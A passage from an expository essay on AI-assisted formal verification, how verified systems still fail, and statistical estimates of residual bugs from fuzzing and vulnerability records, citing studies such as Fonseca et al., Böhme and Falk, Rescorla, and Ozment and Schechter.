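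The proof attempts exposed hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed. One was a buffer overflow in libexpat, a library for reading XML files. Others appear only with inputs of tens of megabytes, which fuzzers rarely try because large inputs slow each run. A proof can treat the input length as a variable n, so long inputs need not be harder to cover than short ones.

Suppose somebody plants seven bugs in a library, each of which can crash the harness on some input under 64 MB. Random testing might miss five of them, but a completed proof could not miss any. This has more to do with logic than with Claude's skill, because the no-crash theorem is false while any bug remains, and a sound checker will not accept a proof of a false theorem.

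Anthropic sells Claude and has an interest in a good result. But anyone can check a published proof by running Rocq, so these claims require less trust than Google's counts of Rust vulnerabilities. According to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026), Anthropic is publishing the proofs for targets that needed no code changes, as well as specifications for targets it could not prove. The 239 are therefore successes from a larger set of attempts.

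### How much the 239 theorems cover

The theorems apply to single-threaded programs with a fixed memory budget, but much software runs several threads at once. OpenNET also lists dynamic linking, in which a program loads libraries as it starts or runs, and abnormal hardware behaviour as risks that are not covered. Most people also run these libraries on x86 or Arm processors, so the theorems do not cover the machine code on their computers.

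Work on that last gap is under way. Eight days after Anthropic's announcement, *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) presented a machine-checked proof about a complete 64-bit x86 program running on Linux. The security firm Zellic believes it is the first such proof to be published. The x86 instruction set is harder to model than RISC-V, but proving properties of the machine code removes the compiler from the trusted base, as in the Anthropic study.

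Lim and colleagues raise a more basic objection. A harness typically calls the library in one fixed order, so a proof about the harness covers only one way of using the library. In their example, a small library opens a stream of bytes, reads from it and closes it. The harness reads once, and the no-crash theorem is true. But the read function limits each request to the stream's total size instead of the number of bytes remaining, so a program that reads 40 bytes twice from a 64-byte stream reads 16 bytes past the end. Reading in pieces is a legal way to use the library, but the theorem does not cover it.

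The Anthropic study also included proofs with more demanding specifications. According to OpenNET, Claude proved that the zlib code in the Linux kernel conforms to RFC 1950, the standard for that compression format. It also wrote an interpreter in Rust for part of Python and proved that the interpreter follows a formal description of CPython's behavior. Python has no precise official definition to prove against, so the researchers compared the interpreter with CPython on more than 1.7 million random programs. The two agreed on 99.95 percent of them, and the roughly 850 disagreements were all in known edge cases.

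### Signal's encryption

In *AlphaProof Code*, Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026) at Google DeepMind set out to prove that the compiled code of libsignal, the reference implementation of the protocol behind the messaging app Signal, protects messages. libsignal is mostly written in Rust, which already excludes most memory errors but does not prevent a programmer from reusing a key or skipping a signature check.

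Chaudhuri and colleagues' system has an agent that writes specifications in Lean under human guidance, a model of AArch64 (the instruction set of 64-bit Arm processors, found in most phones), and a team of agents that write proofs without help. The proofs cover the handshake in which two phones agree on their first keys, and the "ratchet" that keeps replacing those keys as the conversation goes on. They establish handshake secrecy, meaning that an eavesdropper cannot learn the agreed keys, and authentication, meaning that each side is talking to the right partner. They also establish forward secrecy, meaning that someone who steals the current keys cannot read earlier messages, and post-compromise security, meaning that the conversation can become private again after a theft.

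Some of the proofs are symbolic. They assume that encryption cannot be broken without the key, and show that an attacker cannot learn the secret by intercepting and rearranging messages. Others are computational. They model the attacker as an algorithm with limited computing time and bound its chance of success, usually by assuming that some mathematical problem is hard to solve.

The agents produced about 6.5 million lines of Lean. The description of the announcement, *Formal Verification of Signal’s Protocol with Gemini* (Kohli and Chaudhuri, 2026), gives the figure as "over three million", which is compatible but oddly low. The theorems depend on about 26,000 lines of trusted specifications and processor model. That is only 0.4 percent of the total, but it is three times as long as seL4's C code, and a mistake in it could make the theorems weaker than they look.

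Schock (2026) reports in *AlphaProof Code* that the process took four weeks. He also describes a test in which DeepMind put two old, repaired bugs back into a separate copy of the code. In both cases the system produced a checked proof that the altered version was insecure. Two known bugs are a small sample, but the test gives some reason to think the specifications are strict enough to catch real mistakes.

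Chaudhuri and colleagues describe their results as the first proofs to connect security guarantees for a whole protocol with the unmodified code of a widely used implementation. They verified a harness for one-to-one sessions and messages, not all of libsignal, as EconoTimes' *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (2026) notes.

### Cost per line, then and now

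| | seL4 | Anthropic and Theorem | AlphaProof Code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Published | 2009 | 2026 | 2026 |
| Verified code | 8,700 lines of C | 239 RISC-V programs | One AArch64 program |
| Property | Follows a full specification | Never crashes on inputs under 64 MB | Keeps messages secret and authentic |
| Lines of proof | 200,000 | About 180 million | About 6.5 million |
| Time | 20 person-years | A few weeks | Four weeks |

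The Anthropic study's page lists fifteen authors. If all of them worked on it full time for eight weeks, which is probably an overestimate, the study took 600 working days. If a typical program has 18,000 instructions, the study's 239 programs have about 4.3 million. If one line of C becomes ten instructions, which is a guess, the study verified the equivalent of 430,000 lines. By this rough estimate, each line took about 40 seconds of human work. For seL4, each line took four hours, about 360 times as long.

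This comparison overstates the newer work's advantage. Each program contains its own copy of the standard C library, so the 4.3 million instructions include a lot of repetition. If nine tenths of them were repeats, the ratio would fall to 36. The estimate also leaves out the time Theorem had already spent on its model of RISC-V. "Never crashes" is a much weaker property than seL4's functional correctness, so part of the reduction in effort comes from proving less.

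Computing costs come on top of the labour. AI companies charge by the token, a fragment of text. At an assumed ten tokens a line, 180 million lines come to 1.8 billion tokens, not counting failed attempts. The improvements that Lim and colleagues say the method needs include a lower token cost and the reuse of proofs for code that several libraries share. A patch or a new release changes the machine code, so at least part of the proof needs redoing. Rust's compiler, by contrast, repeats its checks on every build at almost no cost.

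category.xyz's *finding bugs that frontier models miss* gives a more direct comparison, although it involves a guess. It describes a Rocq proof that every transaction a blockchain accepts can pay its fees. The proof took four person-weeks by hand in July 2025, when AI agents were still poor at Rocq. The developers would not be surprised if agents could now do more than 95 percent of the work, leaving about one day for a human.

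### Kleppmann's prediction, a year later

In December 2025 Martin Kleppmann, a computer scientist, predicted that AI would bring formal verification into mainstream software engineering. He argued that for most systems, bugs had cost less than the proofs that would have prevented them, and that AI was about to make the proofs vastly cheaper. At the time a specialist still had to guide the work, but Kleppmann expected full automation within a few years. Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It*, from the early days of Anthropic's coding agent, compares the specialist's role to a project manager's.

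His prediction about cost came true sooner than he expected. Within eleven months, Claude was writing proofs of 600,000 lines that needed essentially no manual review.

It is harder to justify calling formal verification mainstream. Keles thinks AI has already made it so, citing a boom in startups and interest from leading developers of coding tools. But that interest doesn't show widespread use, and the large results of 2026 came from AI companies and verification specialists. GitHub Next's *PDD Kit* (2026), which aims to let ordinary teams accept an agent's code based on a checked proof, is still a prototype. Kleppmann himself suspected that habits would soon hold verification back more than technology would.

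He also predicted that the difficulty would move from writing proofs to writing specifications, and several people who do this work agree. Lim and colleagues say the bottleneck is now deciding what to prove, rather than how to prove it. Tolmach and Klaus (2026) say much the same in *The proof is in the spec*, though they write for a company that sells help with specifications. They discuss how Boris Cherny, who leads Anthropic's coding agent, had Claude formalise one of the company's software kits. A couple of short prompts led to 16 sets of fixes. Tolmach and Klaus accept that the bugs were real, but say that such a run does not establish that the code is correct.

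Better specifications will also make the proofs require more work again. Lim and colleagues wrote harnesses for 29 libraries that aim to allow every legal sequence of calls, whereas an ordinary harness allows only one. A prover then has to reason about sequences of any length and all the state the library keeps between calls. They released the harnesses as open challenges for AI provers.

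## How do systems with guarantees still fail?

A guarantee has the form A ⇒ ∀x ∈ X: Safe(x), and a system that has one can still fail in four ways. The definition of Safe may omit something that users need. The assumptions in A may be wrong about the environment. They may also include the correctness of a compiler or proof checker that has a flaw. Finally, the part that fails may be one the theorem doesn't cover.

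Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017), in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, found examples of all four. They examined IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, three research systems that keep copies of the same data on several servers and have machine-checked proofs. They read the code, used a fuzzer to disturb the network and the disk, and checked each system for bugs they had seen in the others. They found 16 bugs: 11 in the shim layer, the unverified code that connects the verified part to the network and the disk, three in the verification tools, and two in the specifications. In more than eight months, they found none in the protocols, the intricate rules that keep the servers in agreement.

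### What a specification leaves out

A client that gets no answer from a server sends its request again, because the network may have lost the first one. The server has to detect the repeat, or a bank transfer could go through twice. IronFleet's servers did detect repeats, but its specification did not require them to. Fonseca and colleagues changed seven lines of the program to switch this feature off, and the altered version still passed verification.

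IronFleet's developers confirmed the gap but did not consider it a bug. They had proved linearizability, which roughly means that the results look as if the requests ran one at a time, and they interpreted this as allowing a request to run twice. The released program did remove duplicates, so the gap harmed nobody. But a later programmer could have broken that feature, and the verifier would not have detected it.

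Fonseca and colleagues wrote a tool that searches for such gaps by disabling random pieces of a program and rerunning the verifier. If the program still verifies after losing a feature, the specification probably omits that feature. The average number of attempts the tool took to rediscover IronFleet's gap ranged from 18 to 8,015, depending on the function they targeted.

When AI writes the specification, the gap can be harder to spot. Tolmach and Klaus describe a test in which Kimina, a model that translates mathematics into Lean, was given a deliberately false step: if 3ˣ = 5, then 3ˣ⁺² = 51. (The right answer is 45.) Kimina declared x to be a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3ˣ = 5, so the theorem is true only because its condition never holds, and Lean will accept a proof of it. They also cite an agent that got 89.5 percent of graduate-level statements to compile in Lean but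 translated only 60.5 percent faithfully, so about a third of the statements that compiled differed in meaning from the originals.

### When the environment differs from the model

Chapar's developers had proved causal consistency, which is supposed to prevent anyone from seeing an effect without its cause. But the algorithms that Chapar implements assume a reliable network, and its servers sent each other updates over UDP, an internet protocol that can drop, repeat or reorder packets. Fonseca and colleagues constructed a case in which a repeated packet violates this guarantee. One client stores "NA" under a key and then replaces it with "Request". A second client reads "Request" and stores "Reply" under another key. If the network delivers the "NA" packet a second time, the server applies it again, and a third client sees the reply but not the request.

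A lost packet also meant that clients of the receiving server never saw the update it carried, and sometimes missed later ones too. The developers replied, correctly, that their theorem guarantees causal consistency if the network behaves as their model assumes, but UDP doesn't behave that way.

A formal model can also misdescribe the program itself. Tolmach and Klaus report that researchers asked Claude for a formal model of etcd, a widely used database that follows a protocol called Raft. Claude returned essentially the model printed in the appendix of the original Raft paper. It passed every check but had little to do with etcd's code.

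### Flaws in the trusted base

IronFleet's build tool, NuBuild, ran the verifier on each file and read the messages it printed. If the underlying prover crashed, the verifier first printed an error count that left out the crash, then a separate message about it. NuBuild stopped reading after the count, so after a crash it would accept and build any program, even one that asserted a falsehood. Such crashes were a real risk because IronFleet's own download paired the prover with incompatible libraries. The mistake was in a few lines of text processing, outside the part of the verifier that reasons about proofs.

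Rust depends on a much larger trusted base. Its standard library offers functions that safe code can call freely, but many of them use `unsafe` code internally. Bae, of Microsoft's FORGE Lab, used an AI scanning system called Hyenas to look for memory flaws there and found several, including some that a program written entirely in safe Rust can trigger. He groups them into three patterns of misplaced trust:

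- **Trusting code not to panic.** A panic is Rust's orderly way of stopping after an error, during which clean-up code runs. If unsafe code has briefly left two records pointing to the same memory when a panic occurs, the clean-up may free that memory twice.
- **Trusting code that users supply.** A library function might ask a user's data type how many items it holds and reserve space for that many. If the type reports three and then delivers five, the function writes past the end unless it checks.
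- **Trusting the underlying system.** The library may rely on the operating system to behave in a way that it does not always behave.

The examples under the first two patterns are generic illustrations, not the specific bugs. Bae considers those two patterns familiar but still hard to avoid, and thinks flaws at the boundary with the operating system have only now become possible to find.

### Parts that no theorem covers

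*Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes failures in lean-zip, a verified compression library. The library has a theorem that decompressing compressed data returns the original for any input under a gigabyte, but its module for opening ZIP archives has no theorems. A 156-byte ZIP file with a stated size of several exabytes made that module request that much memory and crash. The standard unzip program avoids this by comparing the stated size with the actual file. A similar file caused a buffer overflow in Lean's runtime, which is part of the trusted base. The runtime reserves 24 + n bytes to store n bytes, and when n is 2⁶⁴ − 1, the sum wraps around to 23.

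Most of the shim-layer bugs that Fonseca and colleagues found also belong here. Verdi's server, for example, used spaces and line breaks to separate commands but did not neutralise them in client data, so a client could hide extra commands inside an ordinary request. Nine of the eleven shim-layer bugs could crash or hang a server. One of those crashes occurred in code generated from the verified program, whose proof covered its results but not its memory use. When one server had fallen more than 500,000 requests behind, another ran out of stack memory trying to list the requests the first had missed.

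### Searching by trying to prove

A sanitizer can detect a bad memory access in any program without information about the program's purpose. No such general test exists for a server that runs a request twice or a compiler that accepts a program it should reject. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) is about these logic bugs, in which software breaks an implicit rule, or invariant.

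Anthropic tried four ways of finding logic bugs with language models, and the simplest worked best. Faisal identifies the two best methods as agentic code review and informal correctness proofs. In agentic code review, a model reads the source code and looks for flaws. In an informal correctness proof, it tries to argue that the code is correct, and each place where the argument fails is a possible bug. The researchers first tested the methods on 21 logic bugs that developers had already patched. Without hints, code review found 11 and informal proofs found 8, a difference small enough to be due to chance. When the researchers supplied the invariants, informal proofs found all 21.

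That perfect score probably overstates how well the method would work on new code, because someone writing an invariant for a patched bug can already know which rule the bug broke. Still, the increase from 8 to 21 suggests that the models could usually carry out the argument but often lacked a statement of what to prove. Searching for logic bugs needs a specification nearly as much as verification does.

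Linux's eBPF verifier shows why a failed proof is so useful for locating bugs. eBPF lets users run small programs inside the Linux kernel, and the verifier must reject any program that might access forbidden memory. It does this by calculating a range of possible values for each number in the program. A proof that the verifier is sound shows, for each instruction, that if the range contains the true value before the instruction runs, the updated range contains the true value afterwards.

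A hypothetical verifier works on eight-bit numbers, which run from 0 to 255. If x is between 250 and 255 and y is between 0 and 10, the obvious rule for addition puts x + y between 250 and 265. But 250 + 10 wraps around to 4. The addition rule can be proved correct only if the code handles sums above 255. If it doesn't, the person or model attempting the proof gets stuck at the faulty rule and can read off values that trigger the error. A reviewer might miss the error because the rule is correct for ordinary arithmetic.

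According to Faisal, Anthropic used informal proofs to find more than 100 soundness bugs in the real eBPF verifier. Similarly, when engineers wrote precise specifications and proof obligations for category.xyz's blockchain software, they found several bugs that ordinary review had missed. An informal proof is too unreliable to support a guarantee, because nobody has checked each step mechanically. This matters much less for finding bugs, because if the model wrongly reports a gap, someone can run the supposed counterexample and see that nothing goes wrong.

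Anthropic also asked Claude to prove that safe Rust code is type-safe, and got several dozen counterexamples. One is a five-line program that borrows an element of a two-dimensional array. While the program computes the element's second index, it moves the inner array and frees it, which leaves the reference pointing at freed memory. The compiler should reject this program but has accepted it since April 2019, when Rust switched to more flexible borrowing rules. The bug was still open on 3 December 2026, along with about 178 other soundness issues.

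How much such a compiler flaw matters depends on the threat model. *What the 11-year-old Rust borrow checker bug means* (Owen, 2026) describes another one, which the Rust project says only deliberately malicious code could exploit. Rust mainly protects programmers from their own mistakes, and few people write such strange code by accident. Anthropic likewise calls its Rust findings bugs and not vulnerabilities in the traditional sense. Flaws in the eBPF verifier matter more, because it is supposed to stop dangerous programs whether or not the harm is intended.

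### Bug reports and claims of verification

Keles argues that people can check a bug report much more easily than a claim that software is verified. The report includes evidence they can examine, such as a file that crashes the program. A machine checks the proof of a verified program, but people still have to judge the definitions, the model of the program and the prover. Since the claim covers every input, a mistake in any of these can invalidate it.

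Specialists could once call CompCert "a verified compiler" without much trouble, because proofs took years and experts reviewed them closely. Keles guesses that AI has since multiplied the amount of "formally verified software" by perhaps a thousand, far more than experts can review. He wants people to replace that phrase with "verifying X properties of Y". The description of lean-zip would then be "verified that decompression reverses compression for inputs under a gigabyte", which wouldn't lead readers to assume that the archive module was safe.

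This is good advice, though Keles overstates how easy it is to check reports of logic errors. Nicholas Carlini, one of the Anthropic researchers, is not a Rust expert, so he had to ask developers who were before he filed the compiler bug. When there is no agreed specification, people can also dispute a failure as easily as a guarantee. IronFleet's developers understood what Fonseca and colleagues had shown them but disagreed that it was a bug.

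### How far the measured reductions hold up

Defenders of guarantees can reply that the failures are concentrated in a small area, which engineers can search, shrink or prove correct. Fonseca and colleagues found their bugs at the edges of the verified code, in components of typically a few hundred lines. Their testing kit, which targets those edges, detects 13 of the 16 bugs. IronFleet had the fewest unverified components of the three systems and no shim-layer bugs. But Fonseca and colleagues concede that they focused on the systems' own code and specifications, so they may have missed bugs elsewhere in the trusted base.

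Proofs about machine code, such as those by Anthropic and Theorem, remove the compiler from the base. Keles welcomes this but thinks it solves only a small part of the problem, because the base still includes models of the processor and of Linux. Other engineers are proving parts of the base correct. *Verifying the Rust Standard Library* describes an open project that checks the library for some kinds of memory error, including out-of-bounds access, and is to its authors' knowledge the largest verification campaign for any software library. Neither approach helps when a specification omits something, because there is no more authoritative document to prove the specification against.

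Verification also works as a second line of defence. Fonseca and colleagues point out that a verified component can break a proved property only if the programmer makes a mistake and the specification or the verifier has a matching flaw that hides it. In a hypothetical case where one component in ten has a mistake and verification misses one mistake in twenty, one component in 200 has an undetected mistake. This calculation assumes that the two errors are independent, so it is much less reassuring when one AI model writes the code, the specification and the proof, because a single misunderstanding can then affect all three. Tolmach and Klaus add that an agent rewarded for completing a proof has an incentive to weaken the theorem.

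The new Rust flaws barely change the measured reduction in memory-safety vulnerabilities. Android's count of one near-miss in five million lines would include a memory vulnerability from the application, the library or the compiler, so any library or compiler flaw that ordinary code often triggered should already have shown up. The raw number of Rust flaws is also a poor guide. Kobzol (2026), in *How memory safety CVEs differ between Rust and C/C++*, warns that the Rust and C/C++ communities treat potential vulnerabilities differently. Rust developers generally count a library function as flawed if safe code could misuse it to corrupt memory, even if no program does. In C, such misuse would usually be considered the caller's fault. The new flaws do reveal a risk that a rate per million lines hides, since one flaw in the standard library can affect many programs at once.

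Protocol proofs also appear to reduce protocol bugs, but those bugs are a small share of what goes wrong. Fonseca and colleagues sampled 555 bug reports from a year of work on four unverified distributed systems and found 12 protocol bugs, at least one in each system. They warn against comparing bug totals, because those systems are larger and do far more than the research prototypes. Perfect protocols would have prevented only about 2 percent of the sampled bugs, while about 70 percent were in storage and management tools. By contrast, memory flaws made up 76 percent of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019. A protocol bug may do more damage than a typical storage bug, but a buyer who is told that a system is verified should ask what share of past failures in similar systems the proved property would have prevented.

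## What does a search reveal about the failures it missed?

A search usually ends with a list of repaired bugs and a long run of passed tests. Statisticians can use both to estimate the residual risk from failures the search missed, though neither measures that risk directly. Each estimate depends on an assumption about how the testers chose their tests, which often affects the result more than the number of tests does.

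### A long run without failures

Suppose a program fails on a randomly chosen input with probability p, and n independent tests all pass. The chance of such a clean run is (1 − p)ⁿ. Setting it to 5 percent gives

(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p ≈ 3/n,

because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is about −3. This is the rule of three. After 1,000 clean tests, an engineer can be 95 percent confident that the program fails on at most 0.3 percent of inputs, in the sense that a worse program would have passed them all less than 5 percent of the time. If people use the program a million times a day, this limit still allows 3,000 failures a day.

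The same rule applies to hours of operation, so engineers need about 3/λ failure-free hours to show that a system fails at a rate no higher than λ per hour. Littlewood and Strigini (2011), in *Validation of ultra-high dependability…*, recall that some safety-critical systems were required to fail less than once in a billion hours. Demonstrating that takes three billion failure-free hours, which is about 342,000 years for one system or 342 years for a thousand copies running side by side.

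*The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software* (Butler and Finelli, NASA, 1993) concluded that statistical methods cannot establish the very low failure rates required of life-critical software. *Validation of Ultrahigh Dependability for Software-Based Systems* (Littlewood and Strigini, 1993) reached a similar conclusion. Accepting less than 95 percent confidence doesn't help much. If every failure rate is equally plausible beforehand, a system that has run for T hours without failing has an even chance of running for another T. Even odds of surviving a billion hours therefore require a billion hours of failure-free testing, or about 114,000 years.

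Some designers hope to avoid having to measure very rare failures by having separate teams write several versions of a program and running them together. If two versions each fail once in 100,000 hours, and their failures are independent, both will fail in the same hour only once in ten billion hours. But Butler and Finelli point out that this calculation depends on independence. To check independence at that level, engineers would have to watch for joint failures as rare as the ones they could not measure before.

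*Software Reliability and the Misuse of Statistics* reports that IEC 61508, the international standard for safety-related control systems, highly recommends probabilistic testing for software at its strictest safety level, but also recognises that such testing can hardly demonstrate ultra-high reliability.

Even the modest version of the rule depends on conditions that are easy to break. The tests must resemble real use, so years without failure in one product are weak evidence that the same software will be reliable in another. A repair also produces a different program, so strictly speaking the count starts again at zero. The same arithmetic applies to AI models, which is why some researchers try to forecast rare failures from smaller tests.

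### Behaviours seen exactly once

The rule of three ignores everything about a test except whether it passed. A fuzzer also records which path each input took through the code, and those records contain information about paths it has not reached. If f₁ is the number of paths that exactly one input has taken, the chance that the next input takes a new path is about

f₁/n.

Suppose a fuzzer has run ten million inputs, and 25 paths have each been taken by exactly one input. The estimated chance that the next input takes a new path is 25 in ten million, so finding one should take about 400,000 more inputs. If the ten million inputs were shuffled, the last one would take a new path only if no other input had taken the same path, which is true of 25 of them. The next input the fuzzer generates has almost the same chance of taking a new path.

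This is the Good-Turing estimate, which Alan Turing and the statistician I. J. Good developed during the Second World War while working on the Enigma codes. Ecologists use it to judge how many species a survey has missed. In *STADS*, Böhme (2018) applied it to fuzzing, treating program behaviours as species.

Böhme also shows that the estimate puts an upper limit on the risk of an undiscovered error. If no input has failed so far, the first failure will be a new behaviour, so failures cannot be more likely than new behaviours. This holds even when a failing input follows a familiar path, a possibility that *Assurances in Software Testing* (2018) raises. In the toy image parser, a 40-by-40 picture takes the same branches as a 30-by-30 one, but only the larger picture overflows the buffer.

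As a limit on errors, though, 25/n is looser than the 3/n that the rule of three already gives. The Good-Turing estimate is more useful for deciding when to stop. A fuzzer with thousands of paths seen only once has plenty left to discover, while one with very few such paths has found most of what its present method can reach. Even when the estimate is zero, the rule of three still allows new behaviour at a rate of up to three times in n inputs.

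Both figures apply only to the inputs that this fuzzer tends to generate. A bug behind the fourteen-character password check adds almost nothing to either figure, because the fuzzer will almost never reach it. The simple formula also assumes that the fuzzer draws every input in the same way, but coverage-guided fuzzers change how they generate inputs whenever they find a new path.

### Two teams and their overlap

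Another method estimates the number of bugs rather than the chance of meeting one. Biologists estimate how many fish are in a lake by marking some, releasing them, and seeing how many marked ones turn up in a second catch. Two teams of testers working separately can do the same with bugs by seeing how many of the bugs found by one team were also found by the other.

Say one team finds 40 bugs, the other finds 50, and 10 are on both lists. The second team found a quarter of the first team's bugs. If it found a quarter of all the bugs, there are 200:

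N ≈ (40 × 50)/10 = 200.

Together the teams have found 80 different bugs, so about 120 remain. This estimate is rough because of chance variation in the overlap alone. An overlap of 6 bugs would have given an estimated total of 333, and an overlap of 15 would have given 133.

The larger error comes from assuming that all bugs are equally easy to find. Suppose a program has 90 easy bugs and 1,000 hard ones. Each team finds 30 of the easy bugs, with about 10 in common. The first team also finds 10 hard bugs and the second finds 20, probably with none in common because there are so many hard bugs. The lists again contain 40 and 50 bugs with 10 shared, so the formula again gives 200, although the program has 1,090.

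Teams that avoid each other's work cause the opposite error. If they divide the program between them, they will find few of the same bugs, and the formula will give far too high an estimate. In practice, underestimates seem more likely to be a problem, because testers trained on the same tools tend to find the same bugs.

### Why new bugs cost more and more

How many more bugs an extra search finds also depends on how much the bugs differ in difficulty. Suppose half of all random inputs trigger a program's first bug, a quarter trigger its second, an eighth its third, and so on. A fuzzer will find about 10 bugs after 1,000 inputs, 20 after a million, and 30 after a billion. Each further bug takes about as many inputs as the whole search up to that point. But finding the same 20 bugs in half the time only requires running twice as many inputs per minute.

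In *Fuzzing*, Böhme and Falk (2020) found this pattern in almost 300 open-source programs, using more than four years of processor time. They ran Google's fuzzer LibFuzzer for six hours on each of 263 programs from OSS-Fuzz and on 25 others with known vulnerabilities. They also ran afl for at least four days on six large programs.

In the runs on programs with known vulnerabilities, the number of extra vulnerabilities found rose in a nearly straight line with each doubling of the number of machines. The line explained more than 97 percent of the variation. For three of the six programs tested with afl, each doubling yielded less than the one before. On the network tool Wireshark, 64 machines covered no more code in 45 minutes than eight did. The XML library libxml2 was an exception, because its coverage suddenly began to grow faster. Böhme and Falk kept fuzzing it for three months and saw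 two successive straight-line phases, so slow progress does not prove that a fuzzer has nearly finished.

However, Böhme and Falk only simulated the extra machines. They ran each fuzzer on one processor and divided the recorded times, so six hours on one machine counted as 45 minutes on eight. Their second finding, that 512 machines would reproduce nearly six hours of crashes in under a minute, follows automatically from dividing the times by 512. The finding about new bugs is a real measurement, but of how discoveries become rarer over time on one machine. *Large-Scale Empirical Analysis of Continuous Fuzzing* (2025) cites similar evidence from a seven-day experiment, in which code coverage grew roughly with the logarithm of time.

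Böhme and Falk use a hypothetical case to show how many more machines it takes to find further bugs. Google has stopped finding bugs with 25,000 machines, so it runs 2.5 million for a month, finds five more critical bugs and fixes them. An attacker would then need 250 million machines to find another five. The example extrapolates far beyond the underlying vulnerability counts, which cover at most eight doublings, but it makes large-scale fuzzing look like a strong defence.

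Böhme and Falk give an attacker with twice Google's 2.5 million machines a 15 percent chance or less of finding a new bug, which seems too low by their own law. Five bugs per hundredfold increase is 5/log₂(100), or about 0.75 bugs per doubling. An attacker who only matches Google's machines, using the same fuzzer with different random choices, doubles the total searching, and so should find 0.75 new bugs on average and has about an even chance of finding at least one.

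The law also assumes that the fuzzer stays the same. Cornelius Aschermann, whom Böhme and Falk quote, objected that the difficulty of finding a bug is not fixed, and that better ways of generating inputs can cut the number of tries needed by orders of magnitude. A new method may need only a thousand tries to trigger a bug that the old one would have triggered in a billion. The old fuzzer's long clean record is then a poor guide to what the new one will find.

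### Does fixing bugs use up the supply?

If a program contains a limited number of vulnerabilities, each repair leaves fewer for attackers. Rescorla (2005), in *Is finding security holes a good idea?*, looked for this effect in a US government index of vulnerabilities but could not establish that it existed. He found no significant downward trend in the rate of discovery for Windows NT 4.0, Solaris 2.5.1, FreeBSD 4.0 or Red Hat Linux 7.0. When he grouped vulnerabilities by the year in which they first appeared, the discovery rate clearly declined only for those from 1999. Even an analysis deliberately biased towards finding depletion gave the vulnerabilities a half-life of about three years.

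This mattered because publishing a flaw has a cost. Many users install patches late, and attackers can use the announcement against them. Let C_pub be the damage attackers do after publication, C_priv the damage they do while only they know of the flaw, and r the probability that an attacker would have rediscovered it. In Rescorla's model, disclosure reduces the expected damage only if

r × (C_priv + C_pub) > C_pub.

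If secret attacks do a quarter as much damage as public ones, disclosing a flaw reduces harm only when the chance that an attacker would find the same flaw is above 80 percent. With a nearly inexhaustible supply of flaws, that chance is tiny, and disclosure does net harm. Rescorla limited this argument to routine reports of familiar kinds of flaw and noted that faster patching would make disclosure more attractive.

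Ozment and Schechter (2006), in *Milk or Wine*, did find depletion. They chose OpenBSD, an operating system whose developers had long prioritized security, and traced each vulnerability through the source code to the version that introduced it. Rescorla had relied on lists of affected versions, which often left out older ones. Of the 140 vulnerabilities reported over seven and a half years, 87 were already present in the first version studied. Reports of these old flaws fell from 58 in the first half of the period to 28 in the second, a drop too large to attribute to chance.

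Ozment and Schechter then fitted seven reliability growth models, which extrapolate from the lengthening gaps between failures. Only one passed their tests of fit and prediction. It implied that people had found 67.6 percent of the old flaws, which would leave about 42. Butler and Finelli had rejected such models for life-critical software, which requires far lower failure rates, but this estimate also relies on extrapolating a curve beyond the last observation. Ozment had earlier estimated, from less data, that the flaws were being depleted faster in *The Likelihood of Vulnerability Rediscovery and the Social Utility of Vulnerability Hunting*, and now directs readers to the later analysis.

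The two sides' data conflict less than their conclusions do. OpenBSD's decline was not exactly exponential, but if it had been, a drop from 58 to 28 would mean a half-life of about 3.6 years. Rescorla's data are compatible with that, because they allow anything from a half-life of about three years to no depletion at all. His FreeBSD and Red Hat samples were probably too small to reveal such a slow decline. Windows NT is harder to reconcile with a 3.6-year half-life, which should have split its 111 vulnerabilities about 73 to 38 between the first and second halves of its record. Rescorla saw no decline there at all.

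One possible reason is that more people were searching. Windows NT spread widely after its release, while interest in OpenBSD's old code may have waned. Neither study could measure search effort. Neuhaus and Plattner (2012), in *Software Security Economics*, found that in Mozilla and Apache Tomcat the number of people committing vulnerability fixes changed in proportion to the number of fixes. A falling count of reports can therefore reflect fewer flaws or fewer people looking for them.

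Longer records support Ozment and Schechter. In *Does OpenBSD and Firefox's Security Improve with Time?*, Shi, Zou and colleagues followed OpenBSD to 2020 and the Firefox browser from 2011 to 2020. Vulnerability density fell in both, though part of the fall in recent versions may reflect flaws that nobody has found yet. New code was not reliably less vulnerable than old code, so the improvement seems to have come mainly from repairs.

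Failures can become rare even when many bugs remain. In the example where each bug is half as likely as the last, infinitely many bugs remain after a million tests followed by repairs, but together they cause a failure only about once in a million uses. The program is then much more reliable for ordinary users, but an attacker who can work out how to trigger one of the remaining bugs can still make it fail, however rarely that bug occurs by accident.

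### An attacker needs only one bug

All these calculations treat failures as accidents, but an attacker reads the code, works out which input will break it, and sends that input every time. The lecture notes *Why Security is Hard* call this "Programming Satan's Computer", a phrase from the security researcher Ross Anderson, because the program runs in an environment that intelligently works against it. Odds of one in 5 × 10³³ offer no protection against an attacker who knows the password that triggers the bug.

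Anderson's *Why Information Security is Hard* argues that defenders are at a disadvantage even if attackers search at random. Suppose a program has a million bugs, and a tester would hit any given one about once in a billion hours. An attacker who tests for 1,000 hours will find one bug on average. A defender who tests for 100 million hours will find about 95,000, but the chance that these include the attacker's bug is only 9.5 percent. The defender would need three billion hours to raise that chance to 95 percent, by the rule of three, or three million times the attacker's effort.

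Anderson considers the objection that perhaps only 1 percent of the bugs affect security. The attacker would then need about 100 helpers, which he thinks changes the situation only slightly. In his view, the attacker keeps the advantage as long as there are enough vulnerabilities "to do statistics", because different testers find different bugs.

That last condition carries most of the argument. If bugs differ in difficulty as Böhme and Falk's data suggest, and both sides use the same method, a brief search mostly turns up easy bugs that the defender has already fixed. At 0.75 bugs per doubling, an attacker with a hundred-thousandth of the defender's effort finds an average of

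0.75 × log₂(1 + 1/100,000) ≈ 0.00001

new bugs, compared with about 0.9 in the previous example. A defender who searches much harder than anyone else can therefore do well, but only against attackers with similar tools. Someone with a different method has a different set of easy bugs, and some of those may be ones the defender would hardly ever find.

Keeping the source code secret does not obviously help. If secrecy slows attackers and defenders equally, the ratio of their efforts stays the same. Anderson reaches this conclusion for the ideal case in *Open and Closed Systems are Equivalent (that is, in an ideal world)*.

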